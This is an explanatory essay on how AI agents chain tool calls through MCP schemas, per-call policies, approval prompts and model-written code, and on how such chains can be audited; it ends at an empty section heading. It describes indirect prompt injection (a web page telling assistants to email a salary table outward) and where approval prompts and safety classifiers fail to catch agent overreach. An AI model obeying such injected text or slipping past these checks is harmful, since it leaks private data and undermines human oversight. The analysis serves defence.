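# Declarative chaining of AI tool calls: what composed tools let an agent do, how chains fail, and how they can be audited

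## Tool calls, typed functions and chains

A language model produces text, so another program has to act on that text to read a file, look up a price or send a message. Usually, the model makes a tool call, which is a request in a fixed format for a program to run a named function with given arguments. An AI agent is a system in which a model makes tool calls repeatedly, with the results of earlier calls shaping later ones. Calls form a chain when a later call uses output from an earlier one. Chaining is declarative when the model or a developer states which tools to call and how their inputs and outputs connect, in a form that people and programs can examine before anything runs.

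*ChainCaps* (Jiang, Yang and colleagues, 2026), which proposes a security layer for agents, opens with a chain that looks like routine office work. To prepare an executive summary about pay, an agent reads a salary spreadsheet, fetches industry benchmarks from the web, summarises the two together and emails the summary to a distribution list. The agent has permission to make each call, but the outcome breaks the employer's rules because the email sends out salary data meant for internal use.

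### How a model calls a tool

A developer begins by describing each tool to the model. This description, the tool schema, gives the tool's name, its purpose and its parameters, and sometimes the form of its output. Here is a schema for an email tool, in the format that the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) sets out:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Send an email to one address",
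  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "to":   { "type": "string", "description": "Recipient's address" },
      "body": { "type": "string", "description": "Text of the message" }
    },
    "required": ["to", "body"]
  }
}
```

The part under `inputSchema` follows JSON Schema, a standard notation for describing data in JSON, the text format in which most web services exchange data. The descriptions are ordinary English for the model to interpret. All of this goes into the model's input along with the conversation, so every tool on offer takes up some of the model's limited working space and adds to the bill, as OpenAI's *Function calling* notes. A model with this schema in its input can then produce a call (without the protocol's identifiers and version data):

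```json
{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "managers@example.com",
      "body": "Our median salary is 4% below the industry figure."
    }
  }
}
```

Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains that the model never runs a tool itself. It emits a request, and nothing happens until the developer's code or, for some tools, Anthropic's own servers carry out the operation. The model receives the function's schema and the result, but not the code behind the function.

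Tools that run on the developer's side are called in a loop. The application sends the user's message and the tool schemas to the model. If the response contains a tool call, the application runs the function and sends a new request with the whole conversation so far plus the result. This repeats until the model makes no more tool calls. A model may make several calls in one turn, so in OpenAI's version each result carries an identifier that ties it to its call. The result may be plain text, structured data or an error message. If a travel tool rejects a departure date in the past, the Model Context Protocol recommends passing the error message to the model, which can then correct the date and try again.

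### What a type guarantees

A type constrains the form of a value. Under the schema above, a call to `send_email` must have a `to` and a `body`, and both must be strings. A call with no recipient or with a number as its body fails the test.

Early models often failed such tests. A version of GPT-4 from June 2023 scored below 40% on OpenAI's evaluation of complicated schemas, according to OpenAI's *Introducing Structured Outputs in the API* (2024). Training brought a newer model to 93%, and OpenAI raised the score to 100% by also restricting which tokens (words or fragments of words) the model could produce. Software converts the schema into a grammar and, before the model produces each token, sets to zero the probability of every token that would break the grammar. The output can still fail to match the schema if the model refuses the request or hits a length limit halfway through. Anthropic's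 *Strict tool use* describes the same technique for the Claude models.

OpenAI warns that a model may put wrong values in a correctly formed object. For example, a schema that accepts any string as an address will accept `everyone@example.com` when the right value is `managers@example.com`. Developers can prevent some of these mistakes by replacing the free string with a fixed list of permitted addresses. OpenAI also recommends designing schemas that rule out invalid combinations. A light switch schema with separate `on` and `off` settings doesn't do this, because a call can set both. These methods only prevent mistakes that a developer can list in advance, so they won't catch a median that the model has miscalculated.

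Schemas for results have the same limits. If an MCP tool declares an output schema, the server must return data that conforms to it, and the client should check that it does. The specification includes an example of a weather tool that returns a temperature of type `number`. The unit, Celsius, appears only in the English description. If a server returned 72 for a temperature in Fahrenheit, the result would pass the check, and a later tool expecting Celsius would treat it as 72°C.

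An ordinary type also doesn't record where a value came from. The body of the email is a string whether its words come from a public web page, a confidential spreadsheet or a stranger trying to misdirect the agent. Richer type systems can track more. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses types that record which capabilities a value retains, as well as its shape. A capability is an unforgeable program value that code must hold to perform a given effect. The paper also wraps sensitive data in a type of its own. The JSON schemas in common use have no equivalent.

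### From function calling to a shared protocol

OpenAI introduced function calling on 13 June 2023. Developers could describe functions to two of its models in JSON Schema, and OpenAI had trained those models to recognise when a request needed a function and to answer with JSON that matched its description. One example in *Function calling and other API updates* (2023) turns a request to email a friend about coffee into a call to `send_email(to, body)`.

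Function calling gave models a dependable way to request tool calls, but each developer still had to write the connection to every file store, database or messaging service. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* (2024), dated 25 November, offered a common standard for those connections. A server is a program that offers tools, and a client inside the agent's application requests a list of those tools and sends calls to the server. Once a developer has written a server for a payroll database, any agent that follows the protocol can use it. Anthropic published ready-made servers for Google Drive, Slack, GitHub and other systems at the launch. Infosecurity Magazine reports that OpenAI, Google and Microsoft later adopted the protocol, and that Anthropic gave it to the Linux Foundation in late 2025. By July 2026 developers were downloading its main software kits close to half a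 billion times a month, according to the Model Context Protocol (2026) project's blog.

The July 2026 version of the protocol also made each request independent, whereas earlier versions let a server keep a session open and store what had happened in it. A server that needs to keep data between calls, such as the contents of a shopping basket, now returns a handle (e.g. `bsk_a1b2c3`), which the model passes back as an argument in later calls. Anyone who inspects the calls can see the handle. The maintainers found that this worked better than hidden session state because the model can also see the handle and pass it from one tool to another.

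### Chains as graphs

A chain is easiest to study as a directed graph. Each tool call is a point, and an arrow runs from one call to another when data from the first contributes to the second. In the record of a finished run the arrows always point forward in time, so they never form a circle; a program that loops leaves a row of separate calls. The salary report looks like this:

| Call | Input | Output | Uses results of |
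|---|---|---|---|
| 1. `read_file` | path of the salary spreadsheet | salary figures | none |
| 2. `fetch_url` | address of a page with public pay data | text of the page | none |
| 3. `summarize` | salary figures and page text | a summary | 1 and 2 |
| 4. `send_email` | distribution list and summary | confirmation | 3 |

Calls 1 and 2 are independent, so the agent can make them in either order or in the same turn. Call 3 has to wait for both. A plain log of the run would list the four calls in sequence without showing which depend on which. *ChainFuzzer* (Wu, Nan and colleagues, 2026), a study of security flaws in agent applications, calls such a log an execution trace, meaning the ordered calls with their arguments and outputs. An investigator has to infer the dependencies from those arguments and outputs.

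How hard that is varies with the kind of dependence. Wu and colleagues call a dependence direct when a later call takes part of an earlier output as its argument. For example, a search returns a web address and a download tool receives it. In an indirect dependence, the data passes through shared storage, such as a file, a database record or a cache. An agent might download a script, save it to disk and later run whatever is at that path. Suppose the agent in the salary example saves its summary as `report.txt` and uses a different email tool, which attaches files by name. The arguments of the email call would then contain a recipient and a file name, but no salary figures. Only someone who knew that an earlier call had written to `report.txt` could draw the arrow. Handles have a similar effect. The basket identifier is visible in every call, but what one call put into the basket and another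 took out stays on the server.

The model can also obscure a direct dependence by rephrasing a result before passing it on. For example, Jiang and colleagues treat `summarize` as a tool, whereas Anthropic's guidance is that the model can summarise without one. An agent built on that guidance would make three calls, and the email would contain sentences that no tool had returned. The trace alone would not show whether a given sentence drew on the spreadsheet, the web page or both. The security layer that Jiang and colleagues built cautiously treats anything in the model's context as something that may have influenced what the model writes next.

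In an agent that works call by call, the model builds the graph as it runs, selecting tools and filling in arguments at each step. Wu and colleagues point out that the sequence of calls can differ between runs even when the inputs are similar. Even if a developer tests the salary report ten times and gets the same graph each time, the eleventh run may include a call that none of the tests did.

### Sources, sinks and prompt injection

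Security researchers mark sources and sinks on such a graph. A source is where data enters the chain, and a sink is where data can have an effect outside it, such as an email, a file write or an executed command. In the salary report, `read_file` and `fetch_url` are sources and `send_email` is a sink. Jiang and colleagues describe a sink by its operation and scope, so writing to a reports folder and writing anywhere on the disk count as different privileges.

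A single tool can be both a source and a sink. `fetch_url` brings in a page by sending a request to somebody else's server, and the web address in that request can carry data. If an agent put a salary figure in the address, it would disclose the figure before any page came back. Wu and colleagues therefore include common web-request functions in their list of possible sinks.

Prompt injection occurs when a model takes text in the data an agent reads as an instruction. The model receives the user's request and tool results in the same context, and it has no sure way to distinguish instructions from quoted text. If the page of public pay data included a line telling AI assistants to send the full salary table to an outside address, the model might do so. Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues (2026), in *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution*, call this indirect prompt injection because the attacker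 leaves text for the model to find instead of interacting with it. In the direct form, the hostile instruction is in the prompt itself. When OpenAI announced function calling in June 2023, it already mentioned a working demonstration in which a tool's output had instructed the model. It advised developers to use trusted tools and to ask the user for confirmation before an agent sends an email or buys something.

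The salary report can therefore go wrong with or without an attacker. In the version that Jiang and colleagues describe, there is no attacker. The agent does what its user asked, and the data leaks because the summary contains it.

### Declarative and imperative descriptions

A declarative description specifies which calls to make and how the parts connect. An imperative description lists the steps to carry out, along with the branches and loops (control flow) that determine which step comes next. SQL, the database query language, is the standard example of the declarative style. A query specifies which rows to return, and the database determines how to find them.

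A declarative version of the salary report could be a list of four entries, each with the name of a tool and the origin of its arguments. The entry for `send_email` would give the output of `summarize` as the body. Anyone could draw the graph from this list without running it. An imperative version could also try a second website if the first failed to respond, or go through the departments one at a time and fetch separate benchmarks for each. Its graph would then depend on how many departments there were and which sites responded. For four calls in a row with no conditions, the two versions hold almost the same information. The difference only starts to matter when there are branches and loops.

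Felendler and colleagues use "declarative" more narrowly. They apply it to ordinary tool calls, because a schema limits what each request can contain, and contrast these calls with programs that the model writes. The term fits a single request, but an agent that makes well-formed requests one at a time is not chaining them declaratively, because there is no statement of the whole chain until the run is over.

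Working systems mix the imperative and declarative styles. Under OpenAI's *Programmatic tool calling*, a developer sets whether each tool can be called directly by the model, by a program, or by both. The program is imperative, but the functions it calls have declarative schemas. An approval rule on an MCP tool can pause the program until a person approves the call.

Designers disagree about what should determine the arrows in the graph, and when. With single calls, the model sees each tool result before it chooses the next call. In code composition, which vendors call code mode or programmatic tool calling, the model writes a program that calls several tools. A declared plan sets out the chain in a restricted format that people and software can inspect as data before it runs. In the fourth design, which Odersky and colleagues advocate, the model also writes a program, but a type checker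 rejects forbidden effects before any of the code runs.

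## The case for one call at a time

When an agent makes one call at a time, the model gets each result before it chooses the next call, so it can change course if a result is unexpected. The client can also check each call before it runs.

If the agent opens the salary spreadsheet and finds last year's figures, it can search for a newer file or ask the user which year to report before it fetches any benchmarks. A program written beforehand would do this only if its author had anticipated an outdated file. Under the July 2026 version of the Model Context Protocol, a server may also respond to a call by requesting missing information, such as the user's GitHub username, and the client then repeats the call with the answer.

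The client's checks depend on the fixed format. Before `send_email` runs, the client has every argument in a known schema, so it can validate the address, log the request, block it or show it to a person.

### The salary report, turn by turn

If a turn is one request to the model plus its response, the salary report takes four turns when the model requests both sources at once and five when it makes only one call per turn.

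| Turn | New input to the model | What the model requests | What a person could prevent |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | user's request and tool schemas | `read_file` and `fetch_url` | salary figures reaching the model; the request to the website |
| 2 | salary figures and page text | `summarize`, with both texts as arguments | salary figures reaching the summarising tool |
| 3 | summary | `send_email`, with recipients and summary | the email |
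| 4 | confirmation | no call, only a reply to the user | nothing, because the email has gone |

Someone who approved every call would answer four prompts. The prompt for `send_email` is the last chance to stop the leak, and it can show both the recipients and the text. A manager who noticed salary data in the text could reject the call, and the model could then draft a version without that data.

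### Rules for each call

Software can make many of these decisions without a person. A simplified policy for the salary agent might look like this:

```yaml
default: deny
rules:
  - tool: read_file
    when: path is in /finance/pay/
    action: allow
  - tool: fetch_url
    when: host is stats.example.org
    action: allow
  - tool: summarize
    action: allow
  - tool: send_email
    when: to is managers@example.com
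    action: ask
```

The list of tools is an allowlist, and the `when` lines check arguments. The first line denies calls by default, so the software refuses any call that no rule covers. If text on a web page led the model to email the salary table to a stranger, the software would block the call without needing a person to review it. It would also block a call that put a salary figure in the address of an unknown website. An email to the managers' list would go to a person for approval. Each earlier call was allowed, but the combination might still break the employer's rules.

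*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) connects this approach to complete mediation, the classical security principle that a system should check every access at the moment of use. If the agent instead gets a broad credential at the start and is trusted from then on, it can become a confused deputy, a program that uses its own authority on behalf of someone who lacks it. For example, a junior employee who can't open the salary spreadsheet might ask an agent that can. If the file server checks only the agent's credential, the employee gets the figures.

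The check therefore has to cover who is acting and for whom. Microsoft (2026) recommends giving each agent its own identity, with a named owner, a stated purpose and roles limited to the data it needs. In Foundry, Microsoft's platform for building agents, an agent receives a limited-scope access token when it calls a tool. In October 2026 the company also announced permissions that last only as long as a task requires. Help Net Security's *Microsoft wants to limit AI agents' permissions* (2026) reports that, with these permissions, an organisation's policies stop the agent from gaining authority its user doesn't have, and higher-impact actions can require a person's approval.

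These checks can run quickly. Help Net Security's *Microsoft releases open-source toolkit to govern autonomous AI agents* (2026) describes a policy engine that intercepts every action before it runs and reportedly takes less than 0.1 milliseconds in 99% of cases. Putting the engine in a single gateway in front of all the tools is convenient, but Michael Schwartz, the chief executive of the identity company Gluu, objects that this leaves everything behind the gateway trusted. Biometric Update's *AI agent delegation via MCP has gaps a Murderbot could walk through* reports that he would instead put a policy engine and a decision log inside every service.

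The Model Context Protocol requires servers to validate inputs, control access and limit the rate of calls, and recommends that clients show a tool's inputs to the user before calling the server. It also lets a server tailor its list of tools to the caller's permissions, so that a model never sees a tool it may not use. Clients must not rely on an untrusted server's notes about how its tools behave, because a dishonest server could label a tool that deletes files as read-only.

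### What people do with approval prompts

The protocol states that there "SHOULD always be a human in the loop" who can deny calls. In technical standards, "should" marks a strong recommendation rather than a requirement, so a client can follow the protocol without asking anyone. However, *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) compared 15 production systems and found that most prompt the user at every command or call.

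Users of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, approve nearly all permission prompts. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* put the approval rate at 93%, and its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) put it at 97%. Those rates alone don't prove carelessness, because most commands are probably safe. Users do push back on some kinds of request, and they rejected 39% of the plans that Claude presented for approval.

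In a more direct test, Anthropic also hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor for a coding study, without telling them which behaviour it measured. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automated classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers were not working on their own projects and had less to lose than a developer at work. Anthropic also has a commercial interest in the classifier. Still, the falling refusal rate is consistent with approval fatigue.

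Surveys of developers support this. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) asked 203 users of coding agents how often they approved seven types of action without close review. Of these users, 64% often did so for at least one type, as did 61% of those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code. Developers most often skipped close review for access to the internet, external services and connected tools, a category that includes `fetch_url` and `send_email`. Those who knew of a security or privacy incident, or of a worrying practice, were more likely to approve without close review (70%, against 43% of the others). These are self-reports from a sample that does not represent all developers, but they make it hard to argue that warnings about risk will fix the problem.

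Approval prompts can tell users too little to judge what they are approving. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents causing trouble with files and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, users had let actions run without approval, and in 31 the prompt had given them too little information. For instance, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows whatever code is in the script to run. A typed call such as `send_email` is easier to judge, which is an argument for single calls to narrow tools.

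Better prompts do help. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, had 80 volunteers make 960 decisions about an agent's proposed actions, half of them unsafe. Each volunteer used one of four kinds of prompt:

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe actions approved | Safe actions approved | Median decision time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
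| Exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Arguments, the user's original limits and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, arranged to show the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from adding information. The gain from rearranging it is uncertain, since the statistical interval for that comparison includes the possibility of no effect. Even with the best prompt, people approved almost a quarter of the unsafe actions. They also took twice as long as with the short description, which would be a heavy burden over hundreds of calls.

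### Asking less often

Developers have responded by removing permission prompts. Some agents, including OpenAI's Codex, can run commands in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits the damage from mistakes, and ask only when a command needs to reach outside it. According to Anthropic, 62% of Claude Code users had also removed some prompts themselves, by either turning off permission checks or telling the agent not to ask again about shell commands.

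Anthropic's replacement, auto mode, became the default for new Claude Code sessions on several plans in August 2026. Tools that only read or search run without review, as do edits inside the project folder. A language-model classifier checks the remaining calls. It receives the user's messages and the agent's calls, but not the agent's explanations or the tool results, so the agent's arguments and hostile text on a web page don't reach it directly. In tests that Anthropic published with the original design, the classifier blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary calls and missed 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond what the user authorised. In the cases it missed, it often identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented.

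Auto mode weakens the case for asking a person about every call, but not the case for making calls one at a time. The classifier can intervene at each action because each one arrives as a separate request.

Defenders of human approval reply that agents should ask for it only before consequential calls. In the salary report, the agent would ask once, before sending the email. *When Skills Tell Agents Not to Ask* (2026) cites an earlier recommendation to require approval for consequential or irreversible actions, and Anthropic still advises people to personally review high-stakes changes to production systems. Microsoft suggests human approval for changes that are hard to reverse, though it has not measured how much this helps.

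*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) gives some reason for doubt. In its experiment, 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the task, such as reading private messages. One group was asked about every action and blocked 59.6% of the overreach. A second group was asked only about the 10 actions that a model had flagged, which included all seven, and blocked slightly less, 53.9%. A third group wrote standing rules for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data. Their rules cut the prompts to about 11, but they blocked around 20 percentage points less overreach than the first group. They had set 81% of their rules to "ask", then approved two-thirds of the overreaching actions they were asked about.

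So fewer prompts did not make people more careful. The test was short, though, and can't show what happens to someone who answers hundreds of prompts a week. The participants also judged fairly ordinary actions, such as buying a lounge pass, and might have paid more attention to one rare request about salary data.

Someone also has to decide which calls are consequential. Yan tested a language model that sorted tools by their descriptions. In simulated bans on each kind of action, the model failed to stop 14% of the tools that the ban should have covered. It also judged the tool in general rather than the arguments of a particular call, so it could not distinguish an email to a colleague from one to the whole company. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115, and found that the practitioners' decisions depended on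 the action's risk and scope, its fit with the task and the environment. They warn that a system should not turn a run of approvals into a permanent permission, because the approvals may reflect fatigue.

The agent must also be unable to override the choice. *When Skills Tell Agents Not to Ask* explains that the software around the model enforces some approval steps, while others exist only as instructions. Another instruction can cancel the latter. Putting the rule in the client, which every call must pass through, avoids that weakness.

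### Every value passes through the model

The other camps' main objection is that single calls use too many tokens, because the model has to read each result and write out whatever the next tool needs. Suppose the salary spreadsheet takes up 10,000 tokens, the web page 5,000 and the summary 300. In turn 2, the model reads 15,000 tokens of results and writes them all out again as arguments to `summarize`. In turn 3, it reads both copies and the summary, 30,300 tokens in total, and writes the summary into the email. In turn 4, it reads about 30,600. Excluding the schemas and the user's request, the model reads about 76,000 tokens and writes 15,300 to send a 300-token message. Caching can reduce the computation needed for the repeated reading, but the model still has to generate every token of the arguments, and a miscopied salary could still fit the schema.

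How much this matters depends on whether the model needs to see the data. If it writes the summary itself, it has to read the figures anyway, and it no longer needs the long call to `summarize`. Copying 10,000 payroll records from one database to another requires no judgement, so reading them adds expense and a chance of error without improving the result. Reading them also exposes the model to any hostile instructions they contain, because text that can give a model a good reason to change course can also mislead it.

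## The case for composing tools in ordinary code

If moving data from one tool to another requires no judgement, a short program can do it without the model reading the data. In code composition, the model writes that program. The idea goes back to CodeAct, an agent design that Wang, Chen and colleagues proposed in *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (2024). Their agents acted by writing Python. An interpreter ran the code and returned the output or error message, which the model could use to revise its program.

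In 2025 Varda and Pai, in *Code Mode*, applied this approach to MCP tools at the network and hosting company Cloudflare. They argued that developers had been using the protocol wrongly by showing its tools directly to models. Anthropic proposed much the same thing that November in *Code execution with MCP*. The programmer Willison (2025), in a piece of the same title, liked the design but pointed out that Anthropic had released no code for it. Anthropic soon released a working feature, programmatic tool calling, and described it in *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform*.

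### From tool schema to running program

Software around the model first converts each tool schema into a typed stub, a small function that has the tool's name and parameters but only forwards the call. A stub for the email tool might look like this in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with types:

```ts
interface SendEmailInput {
  to: string;    // Recipient's address
  body: string;  // Text of the message
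}
async function send_email(input: SendEmailInput): Promise<any> {
  return callTool("send_email", input);
}
```

`any` means the result could have any form. Output schemas are optional in the Model Context Protocol (MCP), and without one the software can't generate a more precise type. The lack of a precise type matters more for a program than for a model, which can read whatever comes back. MCP's guidance for client developers suggests accepting the loose type or having a small, fast model convert the result into the expected form. It warns that the small model may invent or drop fields.

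The model reads the stubs and writes a program that calls them. For the salary report, ten lines are enough:

```ts
const [pay, page] = await Promise.all([
  tools.read_file({ path: "/finance/pay/2026.csv" }),
  tools.fetch_url({ url: "https://stats.example.org/pay" }),
]);
const summary = await tools.summarize({ texts: [pay.text, page.text] });
await tools.send_email({
  to: "managers@example.com",
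  body: summary.text,
});
console.log("Summary sent to managers@example.com");
```

`Promise.all` starts the two reads at the same time and waits for both. The variables `pay`, `page` and `summary` correspond to the arrows in the chain's graph, so anyone who can read the code can see which call uses which result.

A sandbox then runs the program. Cloudflare uses isolates, which are separate instances of the JavaScript engine V8. An isolate starts in a few milliseconds and needs only a few megabytes of memory, so every program can have a new one. The sandbox has no general network access, so the program can reach outside systems only through the stubs. When the program calls `tools.read_file`, the stub passes the request to a broker, a part of the client outside the sandbox. The broker adds the credentials, sends an ordinary `tools/call` request to the MCP server and returns the result to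 the program.

Varda and Pai point out that generated code can't leak API keys under this arrangement because it never holds any. It can still leak other data through `send_email` or `fetch_url`.

When the program finishes, the model receives only what the program printed, which here is one line. If the program stops with an error, the model receives the error and can write another version. If the model needs to see an intermediate result, it can have the program print that result and end, then write a second program.

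### What stays out of the model's context

Composing tools in code can save tokens on tool descriptions and on intermediate results. Anthropic illustrates both with an agent that copies a sales meeting transcript from Google Drive into Salesforce, a customer database. If the stubs are files on disk, the agent can open the two it needs instead of loading the descriptions of every connected tool. Anthropic says this cuts token use from 150,000 to 2,000, a saving of 98.7%. With single calls, the model also has to read the transcript and write it out again, which could add 50,000 tokens for a two-hour meeting.

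These figures illustrate one invented task and are not a benchmark. The 98.7% saving doesn't depend on code. The Model Context Protocol's maintainers use the same two numbers to illustrate loading tool descriptions on demand, which works equally well with single calls.

Keeping results out of context is the more distinctive benefit. In another of Anthropic's examples, a manager wants to know which of 20 team members exceeded their travel budgets. An agent that calls tools one at a time pulls more than 2,000 expense items into its context and has to add them up itself. A program fetches the same items, sums them and prints only the names of the two or three people who overspent. Anthropic says this reduces 200 KB of data to 1 KB, although elsewhere in the same article it gives the size of the raw data as just over 50 KB.

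The salary report benefits in the same way. With the file sizes assumed earlier, the model read about 76,000 tokens and wrote 15,300 when it called the tools one at a time. The program above takes 100 to 200 tokens to write and outputs a single line. The `summarize` tool still processes 15,000 tokens. If the agent's own model writes the summary, however, the program has to print both texts for it, which cancels much of the reduction in tokens.

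Measured savings are smaller than the worked examples suggest. Anthropic reported that average token use fell from 43,588 to 27,297, or 37%, on complex research tasks. Its current documentation reports 38% fewer billed input tokens on a project-management benchmark with 75 tools. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for airlines, shops and telecom companies, code composition cost about 8% more. Each turn needed only one or two calls, too few to make up for the fixed overhead of writing a script and starting a container. Anthropic ran all of these tests on its own product, but it had little reason to publish the unfavourable τ²-bench result unless it was real.

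Programs also save time. Each turn with the model takes hundreds of milliseconds to several seconds, and a program that makes 20 calls avoids at least 19 of those turns. Suppose the salary report needed a separate benchmark for each of 30 departments. A loop would fetch all 30, retry any that failed and stop if too many were missing, without the model deciding anything along the way.

Results that stay in the sandbox are also hidden from the model. Hostile text on the web page would reach the summarising tool but not the model that chooses the calls, unless the program printed it. Anthropic also proposes that the client hide personal data from the model by replacing each email address or phone number with a placeholder, then restore the real value when a program passes the placeholder to another tool. But none of this stops the leak in the salary report, because the figures go out to the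 managers' list without entering the model's context.

### Why a model might be better at code

Varda and Pai also think that models are better at writing programs than at making tool calls. Training data includes real code from millions of open-source projects, but model developers made up most of the examples of tool calls. The markers that open and close a tool call also don't occur in ordinary text.

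Varda and Pai report that agents can handle more tools, and more complex ones, when they see the tools as a TypeScript interface. Designers often give models a simplified version of a service because models struggle with many tools or complicated ones. If Varda and Pai are right, designers could avoid this weakness instead of working around it.

The explanation is plausible, but Varda and Pai qualify it with "perhaps" and give no measurements. Knowing TypeScript well is also different from knowing a newly generated stub. Training can reduce the handicap, as it did for OpenAI's models with complicated schemas. Anthropic's results are mixed. Accuracy rose by three to five points on two research benchmarks but didn't change on the project-management and customer-service ones.

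### Support in late 2026

OpenAI added programmatic tool calling with GPT-5.6 on 9 July 2026, according to Daniel Vaughan's *Programmatic Tool Calling*. Three companies therefore document versions of the same mechanism:

| Company | Where the program runs | What the sandbox keeps between programs | Can programs call MCP tools? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cloudflare | JavaScript in a new isolate | nothing, though a separate runtime logs the calls | yes |
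| Anthropic | Python in a container | files and other state, if the developer reuses the container | not through Anthropic's own MCP connector |
| OpenAI | JavaScript in a new V8 runtime | nothing | yes |

Anthropic's version also excludes tools that use strict schemas. Strict mode only works while the model is writing, but a program computes many of its arguments later, so the developer's application has to validate each call when it arrives.

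Google's documentation from the first half of 2026 describes function calling and code execution as separate tools. In function calling, Gemini models receive each result before they continue, and they can make calls in parallel or in sequence. In code execution, Gemini writes and runs Python with a fixed set of libraries (Google Cloud, *Code execution*). Since March 2026, developers have also been able to combine Google's built-in tools with their own functions in one request (Schmid, 2026, *Combine Built-in Tools and Function Calling in the Gemini Interactions API*). Gemini chooses the order of the calls.

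MCP has no format for a program or a chain. In the July 2026 specification, a `tools/call` request names one tool. The maintainers recommend code composition as something a client can build on top of the protocol. Their August 2026 roadmap doesn't include a composition format, but it includes plans for a clearer contract for tool results. A server can currently return the same output in more than one form, which makes generating stubs harder.

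### A program instead of a list of calls

The main objection is that code composition hides the calls from anyone who watches only what the model produces. With single calls, that person sees a tool's name and its arguments. In the design that Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* describes, the model has one tool, `codemode`, which accepts a piece of code. Simplified, the whole salary report arrives as one request:

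```json
{
  "name": "codemode",
  "arguments": { "code": "const [pay, page] = await Promise.all([ ..." }
}
```

This passes a schema check because the code is a string. An allowlist at this point can only permit or forbid `codemode` as a whole, and an approval screen can show only the program.

A manager who reads code could follow the ten lines above, since the recipient's address is there in plain text. But the model might have written this instead:

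```ts
to: page.text.match(/Contact: (\S+)/)[1],
```

This line takes the recipient's address from the web page, so nobody can tell from the program who will get the email. Approving the line before the page arrives is much like approving `python3 setup.py`, because neither shows the reviewer everything it will do.

Anthropic acknowledges that running model-written code requires a secure sandbox, resource limits and monitoring, which direct tool calls avoid.

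### Checking calls as they happen

Supporters of code composition reply that the program can't do anything outside the sandbox on its own. Every effect goes through a stub, so the broker can check and log each primitive call with its final arguments. When the broker receives a `send_email` call, the address is an ordinary string again, so the salary agent's policy from the previous section would work unchanged.

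The Model Context Protocol's maintainers advise clients to apply the same approval rules to calls from a program as to direct calls, and they warn that approving a script does not approve every call it makes. A user may approve a category of calls, such as creating support tickets, for one run, but the broker must still check each call against that permission.

In Anthropic's and OpenAI's versions, the program pauses whenever it needs a tool that the developer runs. The developer's application then receives a typed call, much like a single tool call but with an added `caller` field that identifies the program. OpenAI tells developers to check arguments and permissions for each call and to require approval for high-impact actions, whoever the caller is.

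Cloudflare's runtime also numbers every call and records its arguments and usually its result. When a program reaches a call that needs approval, the runtime saves the request and stops the program. If the user approves, the runtime restarts the program from the first line. Calls that have already run return their recorded results instead of running again, and the program continues through the approved call. This lets a program wait for an answer long after the original request has ended.

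The method works only if the program makes the same calls in the same order each time. A program that uses the current time or a random number may behave differently on the second pass, so the model has to wrap such steps in a function that records their value. Calls that start together can also break this rule, because they can arrive in either order. The salary program begins with two such calls, so under Cloudflare's runtime it could fail just after a manager approved the email. Making the reads one after the other would avoid the error but be slightly slower.

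So a developer can recover most of the checks that single calls provide, but has to apply them in the runtime that executes the model's program instead of to the messages the model sends. If the sandbox has its own network connection, code can bypass the broker and its log. A company can also add a gateway in front of its Model Context Protocol (MCP) servers, where the broker's requests arrive as ordinary tool calls. Since July 2026, each MCP request over HTTP has carried the tool's name in a header, which a gateway can check without reading the rest of the request. However, none of the required fields identifies the program that made the call, so the gateway may be unable to group calls from the same program.

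### What individual checks leave out

Checking every primitive call doesn't cover the sequence of calls, such as the path from the salary spreadsheet to the email. In a post on least privilege for MCP calls, McGuinness argues more generally that permissions for separate calls don't add up to approval of a task. The user sees a prompt for each call, and an investigator later has to match up the logs by timestamp.

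Single calls have this weakness too, and composing them in code helps with part of it. The `caller` field ties each call to its program, and the program's text shows how one result could feed another. But the text includes every branch the program might have taken, and the logs that Anthropic, OpenAI and Cloudflare describe record the calls it made but not what the code did to values between calls. With Cloudflare's recorded results, an investigator could in principle rerun the program and see those steps.

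Timing is harder to fix. If a program emails 50 managers in a loop and someone rejects the thirtieth message, 29 have already been sent. In Cloudflare's system, rejecting a call ends the program but doesn't undo the earlier calls. A separate rollback function works backwards through them, but it can reverse only those for which a developer has written an undo operation, and sent emails can't be reliably undone. An error halfway through causes the same problem, and if the model then runs a corrected program from the beginning, some managers may get the message twice.

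OpenAI recommends programs for stages with predictable steps, especially when code can reduce a large amount of data to a small result. It recommends direct calls for writes, actions that need approval, and searches in which each result should influence the next. Anthropic has a setting for making a similar choice for each tool, but its documentation describes the setting as guiding the model, so a developer who relies on it should also check the `caller` field.

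If the salary program followed OpenAI's advice, it would end after `summarize` and return the 300-token summary. The model would read the summary and call `send_email` separately. This would add a turn but still keep the 15,000 tokens of source data out of context. The model could notice a bad summary, and the manager could reject the email before any program depends on it. The approval prompt would show the recipients and the text, but not that the text came from a confidential spreadsheet.

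## The case for declaring tools and plans before they run

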